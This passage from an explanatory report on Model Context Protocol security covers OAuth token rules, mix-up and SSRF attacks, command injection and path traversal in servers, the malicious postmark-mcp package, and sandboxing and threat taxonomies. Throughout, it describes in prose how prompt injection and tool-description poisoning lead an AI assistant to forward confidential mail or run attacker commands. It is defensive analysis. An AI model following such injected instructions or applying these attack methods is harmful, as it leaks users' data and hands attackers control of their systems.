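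Audience binding prevents this. Under RFC 8707, an internet standard for resource indicators, the client names the server it wants a token for, both when it starts the login and when it collects the token. The login service records that server as the token's audience. The mail server then rejects the converter's token because its audience is a different server.

Restricting a token to one server depends on the client, the authorization server and the mail server. MCP clients must send the parameter even if the authorization server ignores it, but Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Security Considerations* states that tokens are bound to an audience only where the authorization server supports this. The mail server must also check the audience, or it will accept a token issued for the converter.

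Token passthrough is a related mistake in which a server accepts a token meant for another service and forwards it there. The specification forbids this, even though it would let a proxy's developer leave out the second login. The mail proxy must act as an OAuth client itself and obtain a separate token from the provider. If it forwarded the assistant's token instead, the provider's logs could attribute requests to the wrong party, and clients might use the same token to contact the provider directly and bypass the proxy's limits. A thief with a stolen token could also extract data through such a proxy.

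### Codes for the wrong authorization server

In a mix-up attack, the attacker runs an authorization server and gets the client to send it a code from an honest one. The office assistant deals with several authorization servers, so the converter's developer could try the following:

1. The employee starts to log in to the converter, which uses the developer's own authorization server.
2. That server redirects the browser to the employer's login service and presents the assistant's client ID.
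3. The employee logs in, and the login service returns a code to the assistant.
4. The assistant's records still show the developer's server as the one in use. The assistant therefore sends the code there, together with the PKCE secret.
5. The developer exchanges both for a token at the employer's login service.

RFC 9207 adds the issuer's identity to the response in step 3, in a field called `iss`. The client recorded the issuer it expected before it opened the browser, so it can detect the mismatch and withhold the code. In their notes on the release candidate, the Model Context Protocol maintainers describe the check as a low-effort defence against a type of attack that is more common in MCP because one client connects to many servers.

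Since July 2026, MCP clients have had to compare the field whenever it is present and reject a response that lacks it if the authorization server has advertised support. If the server neither advertises nor sends the field, the client may proceed without the check, which leaves the attack possible. The maintainers expect a future version to require authorization servers to send the field.

### Request forgery during discovery

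At the start of the login, the client fetches a URL that the MCP server supplied, and the document it receives contains more URLs. A malicious server can point these URLs to addresses inside the client's own network. The client then sends requests there that the attacker could not send from outside. This attack is called server-side request forgery (SSRF).

Hosts that run in the cloud are particularly valuable targets because cloud platforms provide a metadata service, at a fixed internal address, that often returns credentials. If the client fetches that address and includes the response in an error message or a later login step, the attacker may receive the credentials.

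The security guide recommends that clients require encrypted connections and block private and internal addresses. They should repeat both checks for every redirect, since a harmless-looking address can redirect to an internal one. DNS rebinding can also defeat the address check by pointing the domain name to an internal address after the check. To prevent this, the client can keep using the address it checked, or operators can send these requests through an outbound proxy that blocks internal destinations. The guide advises developers against writing their own address filters, which often miss the unusual notations attackers use.

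A malicious server can also attack a client through the login address. It may supply script code in place of a web address, or an address containing commands that run if the client opens it through the operating system's command shell. Clients must therefore accept only web addresses and must not open them through a shell.

### Stolen state handles

Handles replaced sessions in the Model Context Protocol in July 2026. An attacker who guesses or obtains the handle for another user's shopping basket can pass it as an argument in their own call. If the server looks up the basket by its handle alone, the attacker will be able to see or change it. Session identifiers carried a similar risk, which remains on servers that still support older versions of the protocol.

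Kale (2026), who builds agent systems for companies, warns in *MCP's new spec turns a planted prompt into a stolen credential* that an attacker could extract a handle through prompt injection. The stolen handle is a valid credential, as Kale calls it, only if the server treats possession of a handle as proof of identity, which the specification prohibits. The server should store the basket under both the handle and the user ID from the verified token, so that a call with the attacker's token can't retrieve it.

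A server without authorization has no verified user ID to check a handle against, so it can only make handles long, random and short-lived. Even the full check doesn't block the call if an injected instruction makes the employee's own assistant use the handle, because the call then comes from the right user.

### How the rules changed

*MCP has tightened its authentication rules four times* (Dhamsania, 2026) lists the versions that changed authorization. The table adds the problem each change addressed.

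| Version | Change | Problem addressed |
|---|---|---|
| November 2024 | No authorization rules | |
| March 2025 | OAuth 2.1 with PKCE; dynamic client registration recommended | Each developer had to choose a login method |
| June 2025 | MCP servers classed as resource servers that point to an authorization server | Confusion over whether every MCP server had to issue tokens |
| June 2025 | Clients must name the server for which they want a token | Malicious servers could collect tokens for use elsewhere |
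| November 2025 | Client metadata documents recommended | Unknown clients needed a registration at each authorization server |
| November 2025 | Clients can request further scopes when a call needs them | Clients asked for broad permissions at the start |
| July 2026 | Clients must check the issuer when the response names it | Mix-up attacks |
| July 2026 | Client credentials tied to the authorization server that issued them | A client could send its credentials to a different authorization server |
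| July 2026 | Dynamic client registration deprecated | Unverified and duplicate client records |

The March 2025 version of the Model Context Protocol specification allowed a separate authorization server, but its example showed the MCP server issuing its own tokens. A week later, Parecki (2025) objected in *Let's fix OAuth in MCP* that readers were taking the example for a requirement. If the two roles are separate, the employer can connect its mail server to an existing login service instead of building another. Parecki reports that the June version of the specification adopted his changes.

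The later versions replaced dynamic client registration, in which a client sends the authorization server a name and return addresses and receives a client ID. The authorization server has little reason to trust the name, and copies of the same application can each create a new record. One goal of GitLab's planning document *Implement Client ID Metadata Documents (CIMD) for MCP Authorization (SEP-991)* is to let administrators revoke a client without searching through many nearly identical entries.

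With a Client ID Metadata Document, the client ID is a web address where the application's developer publishes the client's name and permitted return addresses. Model Context Protocol's *Client Registration* (2026) requires the authorization server to check that the document contains the same client ID as its address and lists the return address in the login request. These checks prevent an attacker from using another application's ID to have the authorization code sent to an address the developer hasn't listed, unless the attacker also controls the developer's website. Authorization servers can accept any client with such a document or only clients from domains they trust.

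Desktop applications are harder to protect because they often receive the authorization code at an address on the user's own machine. A malicious program there could use the genuine application's client ID and listen at that address for the code. The specification states that metadata documents cannot prevent this by themselves and recommends additional warnings for such addresses. Dissanayaka notes that a metadata document identifies the client software but doesn't authenticate a particular running agent.

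The confused deputy attack remains possible despite the deprecation. Dynamic registration will stay available for at least twelve months, and the security guide warns that proxies that support it remain exposed. An attacker could also publish a metadata document on their own domain, so a proxy that accepts unknown clients this way would have the same reason to ask for consent to each one.

Under the July 2026 rule on client credentials, a client must register again if an MCP server starts to name a different authorization server, and it must not reuse the credentials it received from the old one (Model Context Protocol, *Key Changes*, 2026). Otherwise, someone who took over the mail server could name their own authorization server and collect the assistant's existing client secret.

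### Credentials in practice

Published figures only partly show how many servers follow these rules. Kale cites a scan by Censys, a company that maps devices and services on the internet, which found 12,520 MCP services exposed to the public internet in late April 2026. That total doesn't show how many let an outsider call a tool without logging in, and it leaves out local servers, where the usual concern is API keys in configuration files.

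Dhamsania reports that OWASP, a foundation that publishes software security guidance, ranks mishandled tokens and exposed secrets first among its ten MCP risks. Typical cases are credentials written into program code and secrets in a model's memory, which an attacker may be able to extract through prompt injection. The ranking reflects priority, not frequency. Dhamsania also expects servers from the protocol's first year to rely on outdated assumptions, but infers this from the version history, not a survey of servers.

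Some operators are stricter than the protocol requires. According to Dhamsania, Microsoft issues short-lived tokens with minimal permissions even for traffic inside its own network. He recommends that servers fetch credentials each time they make a call instead of storing them in memory at startup, so that if an administrator replaces or withdraws a credential, the next call reflects the change.

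### Permission and intention

Suppose the assistant has a token with `mail:read` and `mail:send`, and the model follows the hidden instruction in the supplier's invoice. The client attaches the employee's token to the `send_mail` call, and the mail server sends the message because the token's issuer, audience, scope and expiry date are correct. A valid token shows that the agent may send mail for the employee, but not that the employee wanted this message sent. As Dissanayaka points out, OAuth records consent once, when the user grants access, and the agent may act on it hundreds of calls later in ways the user didn't foresee.

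Narrow scopes can still block the attack. Checking an invoice requires only `mail:read`, and the forwarding call fails if the token has only that scope. However, the client may respond with step-up authorization, and the employee then sees a mid-task request for permission to send mail. If the employee approves it out of habit, the message goes out and the assistant holds a broader token for later calls.

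In November 2025, Parecki (2025) announced Enterprise-Managed Authorization. With this extension, a client requests tokens from the company's central login service, so employees don't need a separate browser login for each server. *MCP Server Authentication in 2026*, a developer's blog post (Raj, 2026), dates the extension's release to 18 June 2026. The employer can decide centrally which servers its employees' agents may use, but employees lose a chance to notice an unfamiliar server.

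An agent that works overnight has no user available to approve anything. OAuth allows a program to obtain a token in its own name, and MCP has supported this since March 2025. The project's August 2026 roadmap calls for a standard way to recognise agents that work without a user, so that operators can stop relying on pasted API keys and long-lived tokens. For agents that do act for a person, OAuth's token exchange standard (RFC 8693) allows one token to identify both the agent and the person. The mail server's log could then show which messages came from the assistant and which the employee wrote.

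Identifying an agent makes its actions easier to trace, but a correctly identified agent can still follow the instruction in the invoice. Task-scoped delegation would limit the agent's permissions. For example, it could let the assistant read only one supplier's messages, and only until it has checked the invoice. OAuth has a standard for such detailed permissions, Rich Authorization Requests (RFC 9396), but the MCP authorization rules do not list it among the standards they are based on.

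Translating the employee's request into these limits is difficult. If the model sets them after it has read the invoice, an injected instruction can influence them. If other software sets them beforehand, it may lack information about what the task will require, and the assistant will have to keep asking for more permissions. Each token also applies to only one server. Even if the mail server's token only lets the assistant read the supplier's messages, the model can copy their contents into an argument of `convert_currency`, and that call doesn't pass through the mail server.

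## Flaws in server software, malicious packages and sandboxing

An MCP server is an ordinary program that receives its arguments from a language model. It can have the same flaws as any other program, and an attacker who exploits one may be able to do much more than the server's tools allow. The employee's file server is a valuable target because it normally has all of the employee's rights. An attacker can also publish a malicious server and wait for people to install it.

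### Arguments that become commands or file paths

Suppose the file server carries out `search_files` by running one of the operating system's search programs. Its code joins the program's name and the search phrase into one line of text and passes it to the command shell, which runs the line as a command. If the search phrase contains characters with a special meaning in the shell, such as those that end one command and start the next, the shell can run part of the phrase as a new command, which is called command injection.

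Path traversal is a similar flaw in how software handles file names. `read_file` should open only files in the contracts folder, so the server puts the folder's name in front of the file name it receives. But two dots in a path mean "the folder above", so a file name with enough of them leads out of the contracts folder to, for instance, the employee's private keys.

An attacker can exploit either flaw without connecting to the file server:

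1. The supplier's message directs the assistant to search for a certain phrase.
2. The model outputs a `search_files` call with that phrase as its argument.
3. The call satisfies the tool's parameter schema, which only requires text.
4. The server builds the command line, and the shell runs the attacker's command with the employee's rights.

Chi argues in *MCP STDIO Command Injection* that developers can't trust the arguments a local server receives just because only the user's own client can connect to it. Once the model reads an email, a search result or another tool's output, the text in an argument may come from a stranger. The server therefore has to validate the model's arguments as strictly as input from the internet.

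*Tracing MCP Security Vulnerabilities* (He, Patel and Wang, 2026) recommends that servers avoid the shell altogether. The file server can call a library function, or start the search program with the phrase as a separate argument that no shell interprets. It should also prevent the search program from treating the phrase as one of its own options. For file names, the server should work out the full path, including any links to other folders, and then check that it lies inside the contracts folder. A check on the original text can miss a different spelling of the same path.

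Anthropic's own server for Git, a system that stores the history of program code, had both kinds of flaw. It passed arguments to Git commands without proper checks, and an incomplete path check let callers get outside their permitted repository. A third flaw let them create repositories where they shouldn't. According to TechRadar's *Anthropic's official Git MCP server had some worrying security flaws*, the security company Cyata reported the problems in June 2025, and Anthropic fixed them that December. TechRadar knew of no attacks that had used them.

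Cyata ran its own code by combining the Git server with a second server that gives agents access to files. A company that reviews each server separately could therefore miss the danger of using them together.

### Repairs and warnings to the model

Fixing these flaws can take a lot of work. *Mitigating Taint-Style Vulnerabilities in MCP Servers via Security-Aware Tool Descriptions* (Shi, Fu and colleagues, 2026) examined repairs to 41 flaws in MCP servers. The average repair changed 203.6 lines of code in 3.3 files, and four of the flaws remained exploitable afterwards. One incomplete repair was to Markdownify, a server that converts web pages to a simpler text format. An attacker could use the server to fetch pages from inside its own network. A developer added a filter for private addresses, but a user pointed out that it could be bypassed.

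Shi and colleagues propose a defence that leaves the server's code unchanged. Their system, SpellSmith, adds warnings about risky arguments to tool descriptions and has the model reconsider each call before the client sends it. They tested it with GPT-4o and 792 malicious prompts. Without a defence, 56.61% of attack attempts succeeded. Specific warnings reduced the rate to 6.69%, and adding the review reduced it to 0.04%.

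Even warnings about the wrong type of flaw lowered the rate to 9.89%, compared with 21.63% for a general warning, so much of the benefit may come from making the model more cautious rather than from an accurate diagnosis. SpellSmith can't protect a networked server from an attacker who sends requests to it directly, because no model reads the warnings in that case. SpellSmith may help until the flaw is fixed, but the server still has to validate its input.

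Client software and shared libraries have flaws too. Two well-known examples appear in the Common Vulnerabilities and Exposures (CVE) list, a public catalogue that gives each reported flaw a number:

- CVE-2025-49596 affected MCP Inspector, the project's own tool for testing servers. It could start programs at the request of a caller who had not logged in.
- CVE-2025-6514 affected mcp-remote, which connects local clients to remote servers. It opened login addresses through the shell, which allowed the command attack described in the previous section. MCPowered's *MCP security best practices* lists versions 0.0.5 to 0.1.15 as affected.

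A flaw in a shared library can affect many applications. The official TypeScript SDK, a library for building MCP software in that language, originally left protection against DNS rebinding switched off. According to He and colleagues, version 1.24.0 switched it on, which protected applications built on the library once their developers updated. A dispute that began in April 2026 also concerned whether a library should prevent a dangerous mistake or leave that to each application's developer.

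### The dispute over starting local servers

A client that uses the stdio transport has to start the server itself. The official SDKs therefore accept the name of a program and a list of arguments, and run the program as a subprocess. On 15 April 2026, OX Security, which sells software security products, published *The Mother of All AI Supply Chains*, a report that calls this design a critical vulnerability. The report points out that the SDKs run any program they are given, whether or not it is an MCP server. If it isn't, the connection fails, but the program has already run.

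This does no harm if the application's developer chooses the command. If an outsider can choose it, the outsider can run any program on the application's machine. In its technical account, OX Security describes several products in which this was possible:

| Product | How an outsider could choose the command |
|---|---|
| LangFlow | Its settings accepted local servers from people who had not logged in |
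| Letta AI | Its settings page offered only remote connections, but the service also accepted local ones from logged-in users |
| Flowise | It permitted only certain programs, but one of those could start others |
| Windsurf | Hidden instructions could make the agent add a server to its own configuration file |

OX Security says it ran commands on six live platforms and reported problems to developers more than 30 times. It lists ten affected products in a table and marks three as patched. Two of the products share a CVE number, so the table contains nine different CVEs, not the ten given in the heading above it.

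The report's estimates of scale are much weaker evidence than these tests. Infosecurity Magazine's *Systemic Flaw in MCP Protocol Could Expose 150 Million Downloads* repeats them with the qualification that the flaw "could" expose this many systems:

- The 150 million are downloads of the SDKs, which include repeated downloads and applications that never let an outsider choose a command.
- The more than 7,000 servers are publicly accessible, but OX Security did not show that each one could be attacked.
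- The "up to 200,000" vulnerable instances come without an explanation of how the company arrived at the number.

Anthropic said the finding was not a valid vulnerability because it "requires explicit user permission for the file change", according to a reply quoted in ITPro's *AI agents using Anthropic MCP could be a vector for supply chain*. The file is the configuration file that lists a user's servers. According to OX Security, Anthropic also said that the behaviour was intended and that developers were responsible for checking the input. ITPro reports that Anthropic later updated its security policy to advise caution with stdio adapters.

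Anthropic is right that this function is meant to run a chosen program. Most programming languages have a similar function, and a developer who passes a stranger's text to it has made a mistake in the application. The permission argument also applies to most of the code editors that OX Security examined. OX Security lists Cursor, VS Code, Claude Code and Gemini CLI as vulnerable, but says that Windsurf was the only editor that could be attacked without any action by the user.

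The argument doesn't apply to LangFlow, where an attacker could supply the command and the machine's owner had no chance to refuse it. OX Security reports that the Windsurf editor changed the configuration file without showing the user the change, then ran the new command. These products lacked the permission that Anthropic's reply relied on, but this doesn't show that every application built with the SDKs is vulnerable.

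OX Security asked Anthropic to change the SDKs so that users could choose only from commands the developer had approved. Alternatively, it suggested requiring developers to set an option such as `allow_unsafe_command_execution` before the SDK would run arbitrary commands. That option would alert developers who hadn't noticed the danger, but a developer who wanted users to add their own servers would switch it on. The Flowise case also shows that a list of approved programs isn't enough if users can still choose the arguments, so the list would have to specify the whole command.

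Model Context Protocol's security policy draws the boundary in a similar place to Anthropic's reply. It says that a malicious local server can already run any code because someone started it, and that the stdio transport is not a sandbox. But the project's security guide requires a host that offers one-click installation of local servers to show the user the complete command, warn that it will run code on the computer and wait for explicit approval.

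Dive, a desktop application that manages MCP servers, lacked an adequate confirmation step before version 0.13.0. He et al. report that an attacker could create a link that, when opened by the user, added a server to Dive's configuration or replaced an existing one.

### The postmark-mcp package

Even a complete command often contains little more than a package name, and the employee can't tell from it what the package does. In September 2025, researchers discovered a package that sent copies of its users' email to its developer.

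Companies use Postmark to send email from their applications. A developer with no connection to Postmark published a package called postmark-mcp on npm, a public directory of JavaScript packages. According to ITPro's *A malicious MCP server is silently stealing user emails*, the developer had copied the code and name of Postmark's official MCP server.

The first fifteen versions worked as users expected. Version 1.0.16 added a line of code that sent a hidden copy of every email to an address linked to the developer's website. Koi Security reported this on 25 September 2025 and described it as the first malicious MCP server found in real use.

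Infosecurity Magazine's *Malicious AI Agent Server Reportedly Steals Emails* reports that the package was downloaded more than 1,500 times a week. Koi Security assumed that about 20% of those who downloaded it were actively using it, and estimated that the change may have affected 300 organisations. It also estimated that they sent the developer between 3,000 and 15,000 emails a day, or 10 to 50 each. The article gives the starting figure as 15,000 users, but 20% of that would be 3,000, so the correct figure is probably 1,500.

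After Koi Security contacted the developer, the developer deleted the package from npm. That stopped new downloads but did not remove copies people had already installed. Koi Security advised users to remove the package and replace any passwords or keys that had appeared in their email.

The postmark-mcp attack was a rug pull in the server's code, so a host that checked only tool definitions could have missed it. An organisation that had installed an earlier version and refused to update without reading the new code would have avoided the attack.

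### Registries and package vetting

Registries are directories of MCP servers. To test whether they would keep out a malicious server, OX Security submitted a trial entry to 11 registries, and nine accepted it. A listing is therefore weak evidence that anyone has reviewed the code. The test doesn't show how many malicious servers the registries contain.

OX Security recommends using only verified sources, such as GitHub's MCP registry. A registry that verifies publishers could have shown that postmark-mcp did not come from Postmark. But an honest publisher can later add malicious code or lose control of an account, so the employer also needs to check what it installs:

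1. Find the server through the service's own website and confirm that the same organisation published the package.
2. Review the code and the other packages it depends on.
3. Record the exact version and its hash, and configure the host to run only that copy.
4. Compare the code again before each update.
5. Keep a list of every installed server and its version, so that administrators can find and remove a package if someone later discovers a problem.

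Keeping an old version protects against a malicious update but delays fixes for known flaws, so administrators need a quick way to review security updates. Developers can also take weeks to fix a flaw. Among the flaws that Shi and colleagues studied, those that had been fixed were fixed an average of 37.3 days after public disclosure. Those still unfixed had been public for an average of 92.3 days when data collection ended.

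*Security flaws in Anthropic tech 'exposed by ethical hackers'* (Matthews, 2026) reported on 25 November 2026 that the security company Alt Security had found dozens of flaws in software built around MCP. Developers had fixed the five that the company had made public, but many others were still unfixed. One flaw let the researchers get past the login check of a server from Amazon Web Services (AWS). *Anthropic開源協定爆資安漏洞 企業內網與原始碼恐遭入侵* (何, 2026) reported that AWS confirmed and fixed that flaw on 27 October. Outsiders can't check the total because Alt Security disclosed most of the flaws privately.

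### What the vulnerability counts measure

He and colleagues and Shi and colleagues counted flaws that other people had already reported. Padilla (2026), in *Exposed by Design*, instead searched the internet for running servers and tested them. The three samples differ in almost every respect:

| Study | Sample | Result | Main gaps |
|---|---|---|---|
| He and colleagues | 119 CVE records up to February 2026 | 24 flaws in servers, clients and SDKs | Flaws without a CVE number and some known cases |
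| Shi and colleagues | 116 CVE records, plus issue reports from 100 popular server projects | 53 flaws in 45 servers | Clients, private software and most less popular projects |
| Padilla | Servers reachable over the internet in July 2026 | 640 servers confirmed, 414 audited, 68 reportable flaws | Local servers and many that require a login |

**The curated CVE dataset.** He and colleagues searched the CVE list for "MCP" and "Model Context Protocol". Most of the 119 results concerned other things with the same abbreviation, such as computer chips, and they kept 24. Insufficient input validation contributed to 18 of these. The researchers rated 21 of the 24 critical or high in severity, but serious flaws may be more likely to receive a CVE number.

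The paper states that the dataset retains all high-severity cases known from public advisories. But the dataset omits the MCP Inspector and mcp-remote flaws, which the paper cites elsewhere. The dataset also ends before OX Security's April 2026 report.

In their study of server projects, Shi and colleagues ran nearly the same search as He and colleagues and got 116 results. Shi's team identified 35 flaws in open-source MCP servers, whereas He's team classified only 11 of their 24 flaws as server flaws. Because the searches were so similar, most of the difference must come from which records the researchers kept and how they classified them.

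Shi and colleagues also selected 100 server projects, ranked by popularity on GitHub. They collected the definitions of 1,856 tools from these projects and found 18 more flaws in the projects' public issue reports. The other 35 flaws came from the CVE search, which was not limited to the 100 projects, so the total of 45 affected servers does not show that 45% of popular servers have known flaws.

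**The internet scan.** Padilla, an independent researcher, gathered web addresses from eleven sources and scanned them on four days between 15 and 24 July 2026. He found 640 different servers and ran automated tests on 414 of them. The tests suggested command injection in 38 servers and server-side request forgery in 29, but these counts rely on indirect signs, such as unusually long response times. Padilla also reported 68 flaws that he had checked by hand. These findings are more reliable, although nobody else has repeated the work.

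The study's best-known result is that 91.8% of the audited servers lacked OAuth. This figure is weak evidence about MCP servers in general because the method favoured open ones. Padilla confirmed a server only if it answered an opening message successfully, which excluded servers that required a login first. He also left out those that rejected the later test requests.

A server without OAuth may still require an API key or another credential. In the third scan, 106 of 464 servers (23%) offered tools without requiring any credential. Padilla also counted 687 tools whose names, descriptions and parameters suggested that they ran shell commands. He didn't try any harmful commands, so the count doesn't show how many of these tools would give an attacker control of the machine.

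The number of servers also depends on the day and the search method. Of the 464 servers in the third scan, 193 had disappeared three days later. Padilla cites a Censys search on 1 May 2026 that returned about 21,000 results, far more than the 12,520 services in the late-April Censys scan mentioned in the previous section. Padilla's scanner recognised servers by their reply to the `initialize` message. The specification removed that message four days after the last scan, so a repeat of the study would need an additional test.

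The percentages from these studies can't be combined into one estimate. Command injection accounts for 29% of the flaws in He and colleagues' dataset and 51% in Shi and colleagues', while Padilla's tests found signs of it in 9% of audited servers. The first two figures are shares of reported flaws, and the third is a share of servers. Combining the first two datasets would also count some flaws twice, because both draw on the same CVE records. None of the three studies measured how often attackers exploit these flaws.

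### How a sandbox limits the damage

A sandbox is an environment that limits which files, networks and system functions a program can reach. The operating system enforces the limits, so they still apply if an attacker takes over the program. The MCP security guide recommends that hosts start local servers in a sandbox with few permissions and let users grant more when needed. For the employee's file server, the limits could look like this:

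| Limit | Setting | Effect on an attack |
|---|---|---|
| Files | Read the contracts folder and nothing else of the employee's | Path traversal can't reach private keys |
| Network | No connections | Injected code can't upload the contracts |
| Processes | Run only the search program, with limits on memory and running time | An injected command can't start other programs or exhaust the computer's memory |
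| Credentials | None inside the sandbox | An attacker finds no keys to copy |

The host sets up the sandbox in this order:

1. It reads the server's permitted folders and network destinations from a configuration that neither the agent nor the server can change.
2. It creates the sandbox and applies the limits.
3. It starts the server inside. Any program that the server starts is subject to the same limits.
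4. When the server tries to open a file outside the permitted folders, the operating system refuses.

The first step matters because of attacks like the one on Windsurf. If an agent can edit the configuration, an injected instruction can make it add a folder or remove the sandbox.

**Outbound proxies.** Some local servers need the internet, such as one the employee installs for an outside mail provider. The sandbox can block all direct connections and leave only a route to an outbound proxy, a program outside the sandbox that forwards requests only to destinations on an approved list. The proxy also needs the address and redirect checks that the previous section described for login addresses. The security guide names Smokescreen as an example.

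**Credentials outside the sandbox.** The mail provider requires an API key, which a compromised server could copy if it were inside the sandbox. The proxy can hold the key instead:

1. The server sends its request to the proxy without a key.
2. The proxy checks that the request is going to the mail provider.
3. The proxy adds the key and forwards the request over an encrypted connection.
4. The proxy returns the reply without the key.

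An attacker who controls the server can then use the mail account only through the proxy, and loses access when the administrator stops the server. The proxy itself becomes a valuable target because it holds the key and can read the requests.

The guide mentions containers, application sandboxes and chroot. A container gives a program its own view of files, processes and networks but shares the computer's operating system kernel, the central part that controls the hardware. A virtual machine has its own kernel, which usually gives stronger separation but takes more memory. Chroot only changes which part of the file system is visible to a program, so it doesn't restrict network access.

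Anthropic's open-source sandbox runtime can isolate a local MCP server without a container. It restricts the server's access with Seatbelt on macOS and bubblewrap on Linux, and sends network traffic through a proxy outside the sandbox.

A sandbox can take time to start and can slow down programs that open many files. The security guide gives no measurements, and the slowdown would depend on the server and the type of sandbox. People also have to work out which folders and destinations each server needs, and a limit that is too strict will break the tool. Sandboxing doesn't require changes to the server's code, yet isolation accounted for only two of the 41 repairs in Shi and colleagues' study.

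A sandbox's protection depends on its configuration. In 2026, agents under test at several AI laboratories reached real outside systems because the isolation was faulty. Administrators can test a sandbox by running a harmless program inside it that tries to open a forbidden file, connect to a forbidden address and start a forbidden program. They should repeat the test after each configuration change.

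### Misuse of a permitted service

A correctly configured sandbox would probably not have stopped postmark-mcp. The server had to contact Postmark to send email, so an outbound proxy would have allowed the connection. The malicious line added a hidden recipient to each email, and Postmark delivered the copy like any other message. Keeping the API key outside the sandbox wouldn't have helped either, because the proxy would have added the key to the request.

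The same problem arises with any permitted service where an attacker can have an account. If the proxy allows connections to a file-sharing website, malicious code in the server can upload the contracts to the attacker's account there. A proxy that checks only the destination can't tell that upload from a legitimate one.

A sandbox around the employee's file server also does not control what the model does with the results. After the server reads a contract it is allowed to read, an injected instruction can still make the model attach the contract to a `send_mail` call. The employer's mail server carries out that call on a different machine, outside the sandbox.

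## How researchers and agencies classify the risks

Researchers and government agencies have published many catalogues of MCP risks. Most contain the attacks from the previous three sections but sort them by different principles, which can affect who looks for a defence. A company that classifies a changed tool definition as a supply-chain risk may give the problem to the people who vet software packages, while one that classifies it as prompt injection may wait for a better-trained model.

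### Five ways to sort the attacks

In *Model Context Protocol (MCP)*, Hou, Zhao and colleagues (2025) divide a server's life into creation, when an operator registers and installs it; operation, when the operator runs its tools; and update, when the operator has to withdraw old permissions and versions. According to *Same Name, Different Server* (2026), Hou and colleagues place sixteen threat scenarios along this lifecycle.

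Researchers also sort threats by attacker. *A Formal Security Framework for MCP-Based AI Agents* (Acharya and Gupta, 2026) lists four types: malicious developers, external attackers, malicious users and inherent security flaws. The last type isn't an attacker, so a weak file-path check could be classed as an inherent flaw or under the external attacker who exploits it. *SMCP* (2026) uses similar types. It attributes path traversal, which exploits weak path checks, to external attackers, but weak session handling to the protocol's design.

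*MCP-38* derives 38 threats from the protocol itself by examining what an adversary could control, inject, forge or exhaust in each part of the system. It groups the threats by the kind of countermeasure each one needs, such as checks on the text of tool definitions, cryptographic proof of a server's identity, or monitoring of data flows.

*Systematization of Knowledge* (Gaire, Gyawali and colleagues, 2025) separates eight categories of security risk, where an adversary causes the harm, from four categories of safety risk, where the system follows the protocol correctly and still does damage. For example, the office assistant could misread the contract and send a colleague the wrong figure without any attacker. The division doesn't work well for prompt injection, which appears under both security and safety.

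Acharya and Gupta sort 23 attack methods by attack surface, the part of the system that the attacker can reach. Their four surfaces are the tool interface, the transport, the server, and the combination of several tools or servers. They also define four properties that a secure system should have. One of them, tool integrity, requires a tool's definition at every call to be identical to the one the user approved. The other three limit where data may go, which permissions an agent may use, and how one server's data may affect calls to another server.

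Two general methods from software security, STRIDE and DREAD, are much older than MCP. STRIDE sorts threats into spoofing, tampering, repudiation (denying an action when no record proves it), information disclosure, denial of service and elevation of privilege. DREAD scores a threat's severity by its damage, reproducibility, exploitability, number of affected users and discoverability.

*MCP-DPT* (2026) compared six earlier works on MCP security and found that none sorts threats by the component that has to stop them. It proposes naming, for each threat, the earliest place where a defence is feasible and the fallback if that defence fails. This would be more useful to host developers, who need to know which checks they are responsible for.

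### One attack under three schemes

Suppose the employee approves the currency converter, and its developer then adds a rule to the tool's description that all outgoing mail must go to the developer's address. The assistant sends the employee's next message there.

| Scheme | Change after approval | Hidden rule | Diverted message |
|---|---|---|---|
| *MCP-38* | Rug pull (MCP-16) | Tool description poisoning (MCP-10) | Data exfiltration via tool output (MCP-24) |
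| Acharya and Gupta | Post-approval mutation, on the server surface | Description injection, on the tool surface | No exact match; the closest is exfiltration through a logging tool |
| Gaire and colleagues | Supply-chain attack, during installation or update | Context poisoning, during execution | Data leakage, during execution |

*MCP-38* gives an engineer three entries that call for different countermeasures: signed definitions, checks on their text, and monitoring of outgoing data. The entries don't show that these are steps in a single attack, so a simple count would give three threats. The catalogue also has an entry for cross-server shadowing, but it requires a name conflict, and the converter never uses the mail tool's name. The attack worked because one server's text changed the use of another server's tool, and the catalogue has no separate entry for that.

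The formal scheme shows when the host could first stop the attack. Tool integrity fails as soon as the host calls the converter under its new definition, and the host can detect this by comparing hashes. If the model calls only the mail tool, though, a check limited to the called tool's definition would miss the change. The rule on data flows wouldn't help either, because it compares the confidentiality of the arguments with the clearance of the server that receives them. That server is the employer's own mail server, which is allowed to hold confidential mail, and the rule treats the attacker's address as just another argument.

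Gaire and colleagues make the order of events clear by placing the change in the update phase and the theft in the execution phase. But they put rug pulls in the same category as tampered installers, which does not fit this case. The employee never installed the converter, which runs on its developer's machines, so a company that responded by vetting packages more carefully would have nothing to inspect.

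### Terms with conflicting meanings

"Tool poisoning" usually means hidden instructions in a tool's definition, which is how Invariant Labs introduced the term. Anbiaee, Rabbani and colleagues (2026), in *Security Threat Modeling for Emerging AI-Agent Protocols*, use it for a tool whose misleading name or description makes the client choose it over an honest one. Other terms vary too:

| Source | Hidden instructions in a definition | "Shadowing" |
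|---|---|---|
| *MCP-38* | Tool description poisoning | A tool takes a name that is the same as, or similar to, a trusted tool's |
| Acharya and Gupta | Description injection, one of four kinds of tool poisoning | A tool copies a trusted tool's name or description |
| Gaire and colleagues | Context poisoning | A server imitates a trusted server |
| Anbiaee and colleagues | No separate category | An attacker changes the output after the client has chosen the right tool |

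These differences matter when someone compares products or test results. A scanner that "detects tool poisoning" may look for hidden commands but ignore misleading names. Similarly, the 37% average success rate in MCPTox applies to hidden instructions and doesn't measure how often a model picks a tool with a flattering description.

### How the categories were derived

*MCP-38* says it includes a threat only if there is documented evidence that someone has carried it out, in a laboratory or in real use. Its table doesn't show such evidence for every entry. For the threat that an attacker studies a server's tool definitions to plan an attack, it cites only OWASP's list of risks to web interfaces.

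They tested the catalogue by comparing it with other frameworks and with five security products. They did not test whether people would classify the same real incidents in the same way, so its completeness and consistency are still unproven. The comparison also has errors. According to the text, rug pulls have no equivalent in the OWASP lists, but the table places them in OWASP's supply-chain categories. The text also gives the five products' combined coverage as at most 18 of the 38 threats, but the table shows only ten different threats covered.

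Acharya and Gupta built their scheme from 12 papers on MCP and four broader surveys, merging overlapping categories. They report that no existing defence covers more than 34% of the threats and that their own design, MCPShield, covers 91%. The 91% figure means that they matched 21 of their 23 attack methods to some part of the design. They acknowledge that nobody has built or tested MCPShield, so the figure doesn't show how many attacks it would stop.

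*MCPXKIT* (2025) comes closer to a test because its catalogue has a column for how well each attack worked. Some attacks have no result, partly because the toolkit does not yet implement all of them. Such measurements can show that an attack is possible, but not how often criminals use it.

### Risks specific to MCP and risks shared by other protocols

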